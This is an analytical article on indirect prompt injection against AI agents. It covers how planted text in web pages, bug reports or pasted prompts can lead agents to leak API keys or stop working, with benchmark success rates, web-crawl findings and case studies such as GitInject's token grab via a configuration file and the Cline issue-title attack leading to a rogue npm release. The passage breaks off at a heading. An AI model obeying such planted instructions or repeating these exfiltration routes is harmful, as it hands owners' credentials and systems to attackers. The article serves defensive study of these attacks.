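# Exfiltration of API keys and denial of service through indirect prompt injection against AI agents

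## Background: agents, API keys and planted instructions

Indirect prompt injection is an attack on software built around a large language model. The attacker writes instructions into something the software will later read, such as a web page, an email or a bug report, and the model acts on them as if they came from its user. The attacker needs no account on the victim's system and no contact with the user. An AI agent is a language model that works through a task by calling tools in a loop and reading their results. The attack is most dangerous against agents because they can open files, run commands and send messages.

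This attack can lead to exfiltration or denial of service, which begin the same way but otherwise have little in common. In exfiltration, the agent passes an API key or another secret to a place where the attacker can read it. In denial of service, the agent stops doing its job, or keeps working and runs up its owner's bill.

### The agent loop

A small, hypothetical online shop has an agent that summarises web pages. Each morning the owner gives it links to supplier notices and trade news and gets back a page of notes. The agent has one tool for fetching pages and another for running commands on its machine. The machine also holds the API key for the shop's payment service, which the agent uses to prepare a sales report on Fridays.

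Bolin (2026), in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, described how such a loop runs in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. Applied to the shop, it goes like this:

1. The owner states the task. The agent's software combines it with the developer's standing instructions and a description of each available tool. The result is the prompt.
2. The software sends the prompt to the model as a sequence of tokens, which are short pieces of text represented by numbers. The model generates further tokens in response.
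3. The response is either a final answer or a tool call, a structured request such as "fetch the first link".
4. Ordinary software carries out the tool call and appends the result to the prompt.
5. The software sends the whole, now longer, prompt back to the model. The cycle repeats until the model answers without requesting a tool.

The context is all the text the model reads before it produces its next step, and it mostly grows over a task. In Codex, each new prompt opens with an exact copy of the previous one, and the history carries over when the user sends another message. So if the third page an agent reads contains a payload (the planted text that carries the attacker's instructions), the payload is still in the context when the agent reads the tenth. Codex condenses the history once it passes a set length, because every model has a limit on how much text it can read at once. A condensed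 history can still carry forward the payload's effects.

The model can access files and networks only by producing requests that other software carries out. An attacker who has hijacked the agent therefore has to work through tool calls or through text shown on the user's screen, and a developer can put checks at both points. Those checks can cover less than they appear to. Codex runs its own command tool in a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits the files and networks the agent's code can reach, but Bolin notes that the sandbox does not cover tools from outside providers, which have to enforce their own limits.

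### Why planted text can act as an instruction

Once the shop's agent has fetched a page, its context holds the developer's instructions, the owner's request and text written by a stranger. The model receives all of this as one stream. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) writes that these models are useful because they follow instructions written in ordinary language, but that they cannot reliably tell whose instructions they should follow.

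Developers label the parts of a prompt. Codex gives every item a role, and the roles have an order of priority, with system first, then developer, user and assistant. But a label is one more input to the model's prediction of the next token, and it does not stop the model from acting on the text that follows. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 post for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argues that the usual remedies, such as training a model to prefer instructions over data or marking the data for it, try to impose a distinction that the underlying technology does not make.

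*A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) gives the proper order of authority as developer, operator, user and, last, the outside environment. Tool results come from that environment, yet they typically enter the context with no explicit mark of how far to trust them, and most agents in practice give them high trust. Chu calls this "principal trust inversion". *Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (Li, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), written for the AI company Perplexity, lists the separation of code from data, the boundaries of authority and the predictability of execution among the core assumptions that agents change.

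In SQL injection, an attacker types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. Willison named prompt injection after this attack, and the US standards agency NIST (2025) describes the two flaws as similar because in both the attacker uses a channel meant for data to deliver instructions. David C thinks the comparison is dangerous. Parameterised queries prevent SQL injection by fixing in advance which part of a request is a command, so that the database can never run the rest. Language models have no equivalent, and David C doubts that they ever will.

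David C's alternative is the "confused deputy", a privileged program that someone with fewer privileges induces to misuse its access. Ordinary confused deputies can be fixed, but David C considers language models "inherently confusable" and recommends limiting what they can do when someone confuses them. The two camps agree about the cause but disagree about what a developer will infer from the analogy. The confused deputy seems the better analogy for anyone responsible for a key, because it leads them to check what the agent could do if a stranger were giving it orders.

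Models resist many payloads, but their output varies from run to run, which can favour the attacker. The US Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI) points out in *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations* that someone who can easily try repeatedly is more likely to get through eventually.

### Direct and indirect injection

Prompt injection had a name by 2022, but people mostly pictured a user attacking the chatbot they were using. NIST calls this a direct attack, defined by the attacker being the system's primary user. In an indirect attack, the attacker controls a resource that the model will take in while working for someone else. This attack involves three parties, and the user is usually the victim. *Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (Wang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes indirect injection as instructions in outside content influencing an agent beyond the authority that anyone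 granted to that content. The shop's owner, for example, allowed the agent to summarise a supplier's page, but nobody authorised it to follow instructions on that page.

Willison also distinguishes prompt injection from jailbreaking, in which users trick a model into producing something its maker forbids. He reports that developers who confuse the two often dismiss prompt injection as an embarrassment for the model vendor that doesn't concern them. That mistake is dangerous for a shop that keeps a payment key on the same machine as its agent, because a planted instruction could make the agent leak the key.

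Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) introduced the idea of indirect prompt injection in *Not what you've signed up for*. They argued that when a model processes text retrieved from outside, this resembles running code from an unknown author. They listed several ways to deliver the malicious instructions. An attacker can put them on a public page and wait for a search to retrieve them, email them to an assistant that reads the inbox, or trick a user into pasting them in. A short instruction can also direct the model to fetch a longer set from elsewhere, which keeps the visible part small.

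To test this, the researchers built mock assistants on OpenAI models, with tools for searching, reading pages, handling email and storing notes. They also attacked a real product, Microsoft's Bing Chat, which could read the page the user had open in the Edge browser. They put the payloads in hidden comments on local copies of web pages, so the public was never exposed to them. The payloads steered the model, and in most cases their influence lasted for the rest of the session. Prompts that Bing Chat blocked when a user typed them got through when they were placed in a page, which suggests that its filters checked user input but not web content.

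Greshake and colleagues demonstrated these attacks without measuring success rates, and the systems they used are long out of date. But they reported that many of their payloads worked on the first draft, even with spelling mistakes. The study showed that this attack route existed and took little skill to use.

### Why possession of a key is enough

An application programming interface (API) lets one program use another's services. An API key is a secret string that a program sends with each request so that the service can link the request to an account. Access tokens, which are unrelated to the tokens a model reads, serve the same purpose.

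A bearer token is a common type of credential. *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Jones and Hardt, 2012), the internet standard for these tokens, defines one as a token that any party in possession can use in any way that any other party in possession can. The program puts the token in a header of its request, and the server checks that the token is valid and returns what the program asked for. The holder doesn't have to prove anything else. Many access tokens expire, after an hour in the standard's own sample, while an ordinary API key usually works until its owner cancels it.

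How much harm a stolen key can do to the shop depends on what the key permits. According to *Restricted API keys*, by the payment company Stripe, anyone with a full secret key to a Stripe account can create charges, issue refunds, read customer data and trigger payouts. The thief's requests look like the shop's own. Stripe's *Protecting against compromised API keys* describes this as impersonation of the owner's software and lists financial losses and unwanted changes to account settings among the possible results.

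A key is also unusually easy to steal through an agent, because it is short, plain text that a model can copy into a message or a web address like any other word. Jones and Hardt advise against sending tokens in web addresses, partly because the full address is likely to end up in a log. An attacker who runs the server that keeps the log can read the key there.

### What a leak requires, and what an outage requires

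Willison's "lethal trifecta" consists of three capabilities that together let an attacker steal data through an agent: exposure to untrusted content, access to private data, and a way to communicate with the outside. In API key theft, the private data is the key, and the way to communicate is an outbound channel, meaning any agent action whose effects an outsider can observe.

The shop's agent has all three. Suppose an attacker plants a payload in a trade-news page, in text too small for a person to notice. The agent fetches the page, which brings the payload into its context. The model treats the payload as part of the job and makes a tool call that reads the file containing the payment key. The software appends the result to the context, so the key is now there too. The model then makes another tool call to fetch an address on the attacker's server, with the key written into the address.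 The server returns a harmless page and records the request, including the key. The agent then finishes its summary, and the owner sees the usual notes.

The developer wrongly assumed that only the owner could give the agent orders and that fetching a page was just reading. Every fetch also sends the page's address, and Greshake and colleagues had already pointed out that an attacker can use read operations to carry information out. In November 2025 Willison described a similar demonstration by PromptArmor, in which a poisoned integration guide led Google's Antigravity coding tool to collect cloud credentials from a developer's files and send them off through its browser.

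Willison argues that the only reliable defence is to remove one of the three capabilities, and that the outbound channel is generally the easiest to remove. This reasoning holds for theft, but the capabilities are harder to separate than his list suggests. In his example, a connector for the code-hosting service GitHub could read public posts, open private repositories and publish changes, so one tool had all three capabilities. The secret also doesn't have to be in a file. In one of Greshake and colleagues' tests, Bing Chat persuaded the user to reveal a name and then offered a link with the name encoded in it.

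The trifecta also doesn't cover misuse of a key that stays on the machine. For example, a hijacked agent that can call the payment service could issue a refund directly to the attacker. NIST would class that as a violation of integrity, separate from the loss of secrecy in a leak.

Denial of service requires much less, only untrusted content and a task that depends on the agent. A different payload on the same page could make the shop's agent end its run with an empty summary. It could also make the agent follow one link after another until it hits a limit or the owner notices the bill, which is called denial of wallet. Greshake and colleagues demonstrated denial of service on Bing Chat in 2023 with a payload that told the model to do long background tasks before each answer, which often made it time out without replying.

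NIST calls this kind of harm an availability breakdown, in which an attacker disrupts other people's timely and consistent access to a system. Chu considers it rare for agents because they are seldom the main target of such attacks. Chu bases this judgement on a survey of 116 research papers, so it may reflect what researchers study more than what attackers will try.

The two harms also differ in how long they last and how easily they are noticed. A stolen key remains usable until the owner cancels it, and the owner may not know it was stolen. An outage is usually easier to spot and can end as soon as the payload drops out of the context, but a payload can also persist between sessions. Greshake and colleagues had a mock assistant save part of a payload to its long-term memory, and the assistant was compromised again when it read that memory in a later session. They also got Bing Chat to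 garble its own search queries, after which it sometimes made up an answer and cited irrelevant results, so a user could lose the service without noticing.

Moving the shop's payment key to another machine would stop this theft, but another page with planted instructions could still ruin the morning summary.

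## How often planted instructions succeed, and what is on the live web

The attack success rate is the share of attempts in which an agent follows the payload's instructions. Published rates for agents in 2026 range from about 0.1% to 80%, and much of that spread comes from testers defining an attempt differently. The danger to the shop also depends on how many pages carry a payload and who put it there.

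### Tests in 2025

In January 2025 CAISI published tests of an agent built on an upgraded version of Anthropic's Claude 3.5 Sonnet, then among the models most resistant to hijacking. The tests used AgentDojo, which researchers at ETH Zurich had built to simulate settings such as an office and a bank. The strongest attack that came with AgentDojo worked 11% of the time. CAISI and the UK AI Security Institute then wrote new attacks for this model, and the best one worked 81% of the time on tasks they hadn't used while writing them.

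CAISI also repeated the attacks for five harmful tasks 25 times each, and the average success rate rose from 57% on one try to 80%. If every try had independently had a 57% chance of working, success would have been almost certain after five or six, so the attacks for some tasks must have kept failing. The model tested is long out of date, but tailoring and repetition have large effects in the 2026 figures too.

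### The 2026 competition

The largest body of evidence comes from a public contest that the security company Gray Swan ran with the UK institute, CAISI and several model developers. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports that 464 people competing for $40,000 in prizes made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models and succeeded 8,648 times.

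The organisers wrote 41 scenarios: 18 with agents that call tools for jobs such as shopping or finance, 15 with coding agents, and eight with agents that operate a screen with mouse and keyboard. Four scenarios served as a trial round, so the final rates cover the other 37. In each scenario, the agent had an ordinary task and a conversation already under way, and the participant could place text in one slot in a tool result, file or web page. Participants could read the conversation and knew exactly which harmful action they had to make the agent take.

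That action was always closely related to the agent's job. In one scenario, a user asks an assistant to check for urgent emails, and a marketing email contains the payload. The participant had to get the assistant to mark a message about an important deadline as read and leave it out of the summary.

In 32 of the 41 scenarios, an attack succeeded only if the agent took the harmful action and also concealed it in its final reply. A program checked for the action, and a second judge scored the reply for any sign that something had gone wrong. Dziemian and colleagues required concealment because users tend to read only the final reply. A log of tool calls usually exists, but it is too long and complicated for most people to inspect.

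Every model was vulnerable to some attacks. Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 was the most resistant, with an attack success rate of 0.5%, followed by the smaller Claude models Sonnet 4.5 at 1.0% and Haiku 4.5 at 1.3%. OpenAI's GPT models also had low rates. The rate was 4.8% for Kimi K2, from the Chinese company Moonshot, and 8.5% for Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro, the highest of any model. Participants successfully attacked Gemini 2.5 Pro in all 37 scenarios and Opus 4.5 in 13.

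A model's general ability explains little of the difference in attack success rates. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Kimi K2 score about the same on a difficult science test, yet attacks succeeded nearly twice as often against one as against the other. Across all the models, the correlation between test score and attack success rate was weak (r = −0.31) and could easily be due to chance. Dziemian and colleagues think the model family and its training matter more, so a developer can't assume that a more capable model will be safer.

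Because of the concealment rule, these rates understate the risk of key theft. A thief can still use a stolen key if the agent's final reply reveals the attack, although the owner may cancel the key sooner. Gemini 2.5 Pro carried out the harmful action in about 16% of attempts, but only about half of those attacks also passed the check on the final reply. For Opus 4.5, about a quarter passed, which would put its rate of harmful action near 2%.

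Some payloads that succeeded against one model also worked on others. The researchers reran 2,679 successful payloads against all the models. The 44 that had worked on Opus 4.5 succeeded between 44% and 81% of the time on each of the other models, while those that had worked on the weak model Qwen3 VL never worked on Opus 4.5. One participant's template, with small changes of wording, worked in 21 scenarios and on nine models. These results suggest that an attacker who plants text on a public page may succeed without knowing which model will read it.

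### Figures for newer models

Recent published success rates are mostly for Claude, because Anthropic publishes more of them than its competitors. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports a success rate against Claude Opus 4.7 of roughly 0.1% on single attempts and around 5–6% after 100 adaptive attempts, which the attacker revises in response to the defence. These figures come from an older Gray Swan benchmark, Agent Red Teaming.

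Repetition alone could produce a rise of that size. If each try independently succeeds with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *k* tries is 1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*, or about 9.5% when *p* is 0.1% and *k* is 100. Anthropic's figure is a little lower, possibly because of rounding or because the attack never works in some scenarios.

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, released on September 1, gives more detailed figures. Gray Swan tested the model on a benchmark built from its public competitions, with 1,804 payloads chosen because they had worked on several models. Attacks on Fable 5.1 succeeded 0.1% of the time on one try and 1.0% of the time within 15 tries. The success rate within 15 tries was 9.2% for Gemini 3.7 Flash, the best model from another company, and between 24% and 53% for most others.

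Anthropic left out models that participants had attacked in those competitions, because models do worse against payloads written for them. This makes the comparison fairer, but it also means that every model in it was tested on payloads written for other models. Anthropic warns that fixed sets of known attacks can give a false sense of security, and it also reports a harder test using Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan that improves its payloads through practice. Gray Swan trained Shade on 40 coding scenarios against earlier Claude models, then ran it on the same scenarios against the new ones, with 200 attempts per scenario.

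| Model (reasoning before it answers) | Benchmark, 1 try | Benchmark, within 15 tries | Shade, share of tries | Shade, scenarios broken | Shade, scenarios broken with probes on |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 1.0% | 9.26% | 31 of 40 | 18 of 40 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 4.8% | 2.68% | 27 of 40 | 11 of 40 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 6.5% | 9.70% | 31 of 40 | 20 of 40 |

The probes in the last column are detectors that read each tool result before the model acts on it. They flag text that looks like a planted instruction. The probes helped every model in the table, but Shade still succeeded in between 11 and 20 scenarios.

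The models rank differently on the two tests. Fable 5.1 is the strongest of the three on the benchmark, yet Shade beat it more than three times as often as it beat Opus 5. Sonnet 5, a smaller model, held up best against Shade, which succeeded in 0.3% of tries against it and broke seven scenarios. Anyone who chose a model by the benchmark alone would have picked one that Shade could break in most of the coding scenarios. Shade practised on the same scenarios used in the test, and it could fail 199 times without anyone noticing. Anthropic points out that real attackers usually have neither advantage.

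The success rate also depends on what the agent is doing. On the benchmark, most of the successful attacks on Fable 5.1 were against agents that operate a screen. The success rate within 15 tries was 4.1% for those agents, 0.3% for coding and zero for ordinary tool use. The gap was much wider a few months earlier. VentureBeat reports from the February 2026 system card for Claude Opus 4.6 that all 200 attempts failed in a restricted coding environment, while a single attempt in a graphical interface succeeded 17.8% of the time. By the 200th attempt, the success rate in the graphical interface had reached 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them. The shop's agent is in the safer group because it fetches pages through a tool. If the owner replaced it with an agent that clicks through a browser, the same page could be more dangerous.

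In OpenAI's tests, too, the failure rate depended on how the attack reached the model. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that GPT-5.6 rarely failed when an attack came directly through chat but failed more often when it came through tools and outside content. A chatbot's low failure rate is therefore weak evidence that an agent built on the same model will resist attacks.

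Newer models have continued to improve. Anthropic's *System Card* for Claude Opus 5.5 (September 22, 2026) reports that the model did about as well as Opus 5 or better on every injection test, but refused openly malicious requests less often than the other models compared. *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports progress in Claude Haiku 5.5, which Anthropic designed for quick, repetitive work. That progress may matter more than another gain in the most capable models, because a cheap, fast model is the natural choice for reading hundreds of web pages a day. In November, Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) announced the successors to Fable 5.1 and its sister model.

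### How 0.1% and 80% can both be true

In 2026, the security researcher Johann Rehberger got Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to run his code in 60% to 80% of attempts when it was using Opus 5, according to The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code*. On Gray Swan's benchmark, single attempts against Opus 5 succeeded 0.4% of the time.

The benchmark rate is an average over many payloads that other people wrote for other models, and most of them fail. Rehberger instead designed one attack for one product and counted how often it worked. In the competition, too, finding a payload that worked was much harder than reusing one. Participants succeeded in about 1% of their attempts or fewer against the two strongest Claude models, but when the researchers reran payloads that had already beaten a Claude or GPT model, at least half of them beat the same model again.

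The samples differ too. Rehberger tested three variants five times each, so 80% means four successes out of five, and a few more runs could have changed that figure a lot. He calls the results "representative for a motivated attack, but not comprehensive", which seems right, since fifteen runs are too few to establish a precise rate but enough to show that the attack can succeed repeatedly.

Dziemian and colleagues describe their success rates as an upper bound because participants could see the agent's conversation and knew the exact action to aim for, while real attackers usually have to guess both. But the rates are an upper bound only with respect to what the attacker knows. They average over attempts by people of very uneven skill, many of whom were still experimenting, and a small number of participants had a disproportionate influence on the results. A skilled attacker with a payload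 that already works could therefore succeed more often than these rates suggest.

So the right figure depends on the attacker. For text that a stranger left on a page for any agent that reads it, the low benchmark rates are a reasonable starting point, at least for the strongest models. An attacker who has chosen a particular product, obtained a copy and practised on it could do far better, and Rehberger's range is then more realistic.

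Tests against a fixed set of attacks make defences look better than they are. In *AutoDojo* (2026), attacks that a language model kept revising got past a defence called DataFilter 33.4% of the time, compared with 5.7% for the best earlier attack method with the same number of tries.

### One page and many readers

A payload that works 0.1% of the time poses little risk to a single agent that reads it once, but an attacker on the open web can reach many agents. If 100,000 agents read a page containing the payload, the expected number of successes is 100,000 × 0.001, or 100. The attacker writes the text once and never has to choose a victim. Anthropic makes the same point about email, where one message can go to a thousand inboxes and reach every agent that summarises them.

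The calculation applies the published 0.1% success rate to a single payload, but that rate is an average over many payloads. A given payload might work on none of the people who use a certain model, or on most of them. An attacker could expect an average of one hundred successes per page over many such pages, but any one page could produce far more or far fewer.

A success here also means only that the agent did what the text asked. If one in twenty agents had access to a key and a way to send it out, 100 hijacked agents would leak five keys. That may still be worth it to an attacker who only had to write a few lines of hidden text, particularly if one of the keys belongs to a payment account.

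If the shop's agent met one such payload every day, and each independently had a 0.1% chance of succeeding, the chance of at least one success within a year would be 1 − 0.999^365, or about 31%. Whether one payload a day is realistic depends on what people are planting.

### What people have planted so far

Google looked for payloads in Common Crawl, a public archive that takes monthly snapshots of two to three billion web pages. Google's staff first searched for well-known injection phrases. Most of the matches came from articles about prompt injection, so Google had its Gemini model judge the purpose of each match and whether the text belonged on the page, and then had people review the results.

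Most of the real payloads were pranks, experiments or attempts by site owners to influence what AI systems said about them. Some were instructions for assistants to change their tone, add context to summaries, or recommend the site owner's business over competitors. Google considers the requests for extra context benign. Some site owners tried to keep AI agents away, one by luring them to a page that never finishes loading.

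Google found few payloads that tried to steal data, and they were crude. The example it published was evidently a site owner's experiment. Other pages contained instructions for the agent to delete the files on the user's machine, but Google thought these were unlikely to work. It saw no significant use of the more advanced theft techniques that security researchers had published in 2025.

The malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. Google did not publish page counts, so the increase could mean a few dozen more pages or several thousand. Google expects both the number and the quality of attacks to rise, because agents can now do more for whoever controls them and attackers have begun to automate their work. This reasoning is plausible, since a payload that could only spoil a summary in 2023 can now reach an agent with a command line and a payment key.

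The security company Forcepoint was more pessimistic, though its sample was much smaller. *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*, by Sewani, describes payloads that the company's researchers found on live websites by searching for similar phrases. One contained instructions for AI assistants to send a secret API key and not to analyse the code. It was in an HTML comment, a part of a page's code that browsers don't display. The other nine included two attempts to get money, one instruction to delete files and two attempts to make the agent refuse to answer.

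Sewani concludes that indirect prompt injection is "actively weaponized across the open web" and takes the similarity between some payloads as a sign of organised tooling. Google examined similar material and saw mostly individuals experimenting. Sewani's best evidence is the payloads involving payments. One specified a $5,000 transfer and included a link and the steps for completing it, and it is hard to see an innocent purpose for that.

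Several of the others would fit Google's milder categories. One told assistants to credit the site's author and to insert the word "cows" repeatedly. Another sent users to the website it was on. A third claimed that copyright forbade any answer about the page and asked for a poem about corn instead. Shared wording is weak evidence of coordination, because pranksters copy well-known examples from one another.

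Even the API key payload is ambiguous. It included an instruction not to reveal a "flag", the usual name for the hidden prize in security-training puzzles, so the page may have been part of one. Sewani treats the request as attempted theft, and an agent that obeyed it might reveal a key whatever the page's author intended. But a thief would need an address to receive the key, and Sewani doesn't identify one.

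Google's reading of intent therefore fits the published examples better. Neither search could establish how much serious activity there is, because both started from phrases that are well known in the field. A careful attacker would avoid those phrases, and Google acknowledges that its method may miss unusual ones. Common Crawl also skips most social media and anything behind a login, so searching it did not cover private email, shared documents or a company's internal bug reports. Those are obvious places to plant text for someone who wants a particular firm's keys.

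A planted payload also doesn't show that a theft succeeded. Google and Sewani found payloads on pages, but neither reports an agent that obeyed one or an owner who lost a key. The payload in the HTML comment might not even reach a visiting agent's model, because a tool that converts pages to plain text may drop comments.

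## How a hijacked agent gets hold of credentials

If a shop's payment key is stored in a file, a hijacked agent has to open that file before it can leak the key. If the owner pastes the key into the chat instead, it is already in the model's context, and the agent only has to repeat it. Where a key is stored therefore affects how many steps a theft takes, and each step is a chance for a check to stop it.

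### Five stages

Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, divide the exposure of a credential through an agent into five stages:

1. **Introduction.** Someone puts a reusable secret into a message, a prompt template, a source file or a tool's configuration. The shop's owner might paste the payment key into the chat to get the Friday report working.
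2. **Propagation.** The surrounding software copies the secret into the model's context, the conversation history, logs, stored memory, generated code and error messages.
3. **Trigger.** Something prompts the agent to disclose or misuse the secret. This can be a planted instruction, a malicious tool response or an ordinary mistake by the model.
4. **Execution.** The key authorises whatever its permissions allow, such as a refund or a download of customer data.
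5. **Persistence.** The key goes on working outside the agent, the session and the company until it expires or its owner cancels it.

Kenney and colleagues consider the trigger the best-studied stage, but an owner has more control over the first two stages. If a key never enters the agent's context or the machine where it runs, most places that could hold a copy never receive one. Execution and persistence are harder to address because an agent that holds no key can still make a damaging request that it has permission to make. The researchers work for Corvic AI, which makes a vault for agents' keys, so they have a commercial reason to stress the early stages. Their point about the later stages is more convincing because it means that a vault is not enough.

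An agent may first copy a key before or after the trigger. In the shop, the key stays in its file until a payload makes the agent open it, so the agent first copies it after the trigger.

### Where keys sit

| Location of the key | Has the model already read it? | What a hijacked agent still has to do |
|---|---|---|
| Conversation | Yes, once someone pastes it | Send it out |
| System prompt | Yes, from the first step | Send it out |
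| Environment variables | No | Run a command that reads them |
| Configuration files | Usually not | Open the file |
| Logs and program output | Yes, if the output returns to the model | Send it out, or open the log first |
| Stored memory | Yes, if the software loads it at the start | Send it out, or search the memory first |
| Browser session | No | Open a page where the user is logged in |
| Build-server secrets | No | Read the job's settings or files, or start code that does |

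Keys in the conversation and the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions) are the most exposed. A key in the system prompt is present in every session, including those in which the agent reads a stranger's page. A key pasted into the conversation is also hard to remove, because other systems designed to retain data may have copied it before the owner deletes the message.

Program output is a less obvious way for a key to reach the model. Skills are downloadable packages of written instructions and scripts that extend an agent. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) examined 17,022 skills from one marketplace and found credential problems in 520. Of the 1,371 issues the study classed as vulnerabilities, 1,007 came from print statements, which developers use to check that a program works. A printed key normally ends up on a screen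 or in a log file, but agent software typically captures the output and adds it to the model's context, where an attacker can use a later payload to extract it.

*Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills* (2026) found far fewer such leaks in a different registry. An automated search flagged 2,511 skills, about 5% of the total, for printing something that might be a credential. The researchers checked all 433 skills with the strongest evidence and found that only 22 printed a real secret. The rest printed things like server names, file paths or partly masked keys. In a sample from another group of 652 flagged skills, about 11% were real leaks.

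Those figures suggest that about 0.2% of the skills leak a key in this way. Chen and colleagues ran the skills, which also catches secrets that appear only at run time, and confirmed 352 leaks, or about one for every 48 skills. At the 0.2% rate, someone who installed 20 skills at random would have about a 4% chance of getting at least one that leaks. At the higher rate, the chance would be about one in three if each leak were in a different skill. Neither study measured how often anyone stole the keys.

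Environment variables are named values that a program receives when it starts. Developers often store keys in them to keep the keys out of the code. The variables are not in the model's input, but programs that the agent starts usually inherit them. Chen and colleagues point out that many skills run directly on the user's computer and can reach its environment variables, configuration files and network without asking for each credential. Security researchers call this "ambient authority", and it lets the shop's agent read the payment key even when its only job is to summarise web pages.

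A single configuration file can hold all of an agent's credentials. Krebs on Security (2026) reports that the security tester Jamieson O'Reilly found that some users of OpenClaw, an open-source agent that people run on their own computers, had accidentally exposed its control page to the internet. Outsiders could read a configuration file containing every credential the agent used, along with its full conversation history. The exposure did not involve prompt injection, but a hijacked agent that can open the same file would have the same credentials.

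Stored memory can carry a payload into later sessions, so an agent can read the payload in one session and a key in another. Anthropic warns that an agent's instruction files and working folder pose the same risk. If the shop's agent saved planted text on Monday, that text could be in its context on Friday, when it opens the payment key for the sales report.

### Build servers

A build server tests and publishes software automatically when someone changes the code. Many projects now run agents there to review changes or sort bug reports. *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (2026) says these agents have a command line and an environment that often includes tokens and other secrets. GitHub hides some parts of a bug report from people viewing the page, but most agents receive the raw text.

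Isbarov, Suleymanov and colleagues (2026), in *GitInject*, attacked such agents on real GitHub build servers, using temporary projects they had set up. The sandbox or the network rules blocked their first three attempts to take the project's access token. They then found that the standard step for downloading the project's code had already written the token to a configuration file in the working folder. The agent could read this file, and the token was in base64, an encoding that anyone can reverse, so hiding the environment variables would not have protected it.

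Of 69 possible attack routes, 14 worked on the live servers, but the AgentDojo simulator predicted only four of those. Two other simulators predicted none, because they had no equivalent of the file that held the token. An agent's results on a simulated benchmark are therefore poor evidence about the safety of keys that other software leaves where the agent can read them.

The same study found that an outsider could submit an instruction file along with a proposed change to the code. The build server copied the file into the agent's working folder, and the agent loaded it as guidance from the project's owners before starting its review. At least one serious attack worked against agents from each of the four providers that Isbarov and colleagues tested. They tested only set-ups that run without a person's approval, and they changed Google's standard set-up so that secrets were available when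 outsiders proposed changes. The results don't measure how many projects are open to attack.

### Anthropic's exercise with a deceived user

In February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic tested an attack that fools an employee instead of planting text for the agent to read. The researcher emailed a colleague a seemingly normal request for help, with a prompt to paste into Claude Code. Most of the prompt was routine setup steps, but one step told Claude to read the file that held the employee's Amazon cloud credentials, encode the contents and send them to an outside server. The employee ran the prompt. Anthropic then tried the same prompt 25 times, and Claude sent out the credentials in 24 of those attempts.

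This was direct prompt injection, because the instruction came through the user. The result of 24 out of 25 doesn't measure how often Claude would obey the same text on a web page, so it isn't comparable with the benchmark rates for indirect attacks.

Once Claude took the instruction as part of its job, almost nothing stopped it from finding the credentials file, encoding the contents and sending them off. Anthropic's defences inside the model check for actions that conflict with what the user wants, but the user appeared to have asked for all of these. An indirect payload that passes for part of the user's task could exploit the same weakness. Anthropic concludes that only limits outside the model would have prevented the theft, such as blocking access to the credentials file and blocking the outgoing request.

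After the exercise, Anthropic's staff shared the working prompt in Slack, the company's chat system. Someone then pointed out that some internal agents read Slack, which meant the prompt could now reach them as an indirect injection. The staff added a distinctive string to the thread so that they would notice if an agent picked it up.

### The Cline case

Cline is a popular coding agent. On December 21, 2025, its maintainers added a Claude Opus 4.5 agent to their GitHub project to sort incoming bug reports, which GitHub calls issues. Anyone with a GitHub account could start the agent by opening an issue, and it could run commands, edit files and fetch web pages. The software copied each issue's title straight into the agent's prompt. The maintainers had assumed that a title would only describe a problem.

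In *Clinejection*, the security researcher Adnan Khan (2026) describes finding the flaw and testing it on a copy of the project. A title that presented installing a software package as a routine first step made the agent install a package Khan controlled, which ran Khan's code on the build server. This worked in every attempt, though Khan does not say how many he made.

Opus 4.5 had held up best in the Gray Swan competition, where the attackers' text never appeared in the user's request. Cline's software put the attacker's text inside the user's request, where the user's instructions normally appear, which probably explains much of the difference. Installing a package is also normal work for a coding agent.

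The only secret that job directly exposed was the Anthropic API key the agent used, and the job had few permissions on the project. The tokens for publishing new versions of Cline belonged to a separate job that ran every night. But the two jobs shared a build cache, a store of downloaded components that saves time on later builds. An attacker running code in the first job could flood the cache until GitHub discarded the genuine components, then put altered ones in their place. The nightly job would load them and run the attacker's code with access to the publishing tokens. Those tokens worked for ordinary releases as well as nightly ones.

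On this route, the model runs one installation command and never reads a publishing token. Ordinary code steals the token hours later, in another job, so a monitor that searched the agent's messages for keys would find nothing.

Khan reported the flaw to Cline on January 1, 2026, and tried three more times over the next five weeks without getting an answer about it. Khan published the details on February 9, and within about half an hour Cline removed the agent and began replacing its credentials. The next day, an anonymous person emailed Khan saying they held Cline credentials that still worked. Khan passed this on, and Cline replied that it had revoked every publishing token.

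At 3:26 a.m. Pacific time on February 17, someone used one of the old tokens, which still worked, to publish version 2.3.0 of Cline's command-line tool on npm, the main public registry for JavaScript packages. The program was unchanged, but the package also installed OpenClaw. Likhith (2026), of the security company StepSecurity, writes that the company's monitoring flagged the release 14 minutes after it appeared. Cline took about eight hours to replace it, and by then people had downloaded it roughly 4,000 times.

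#### What is known about the theft

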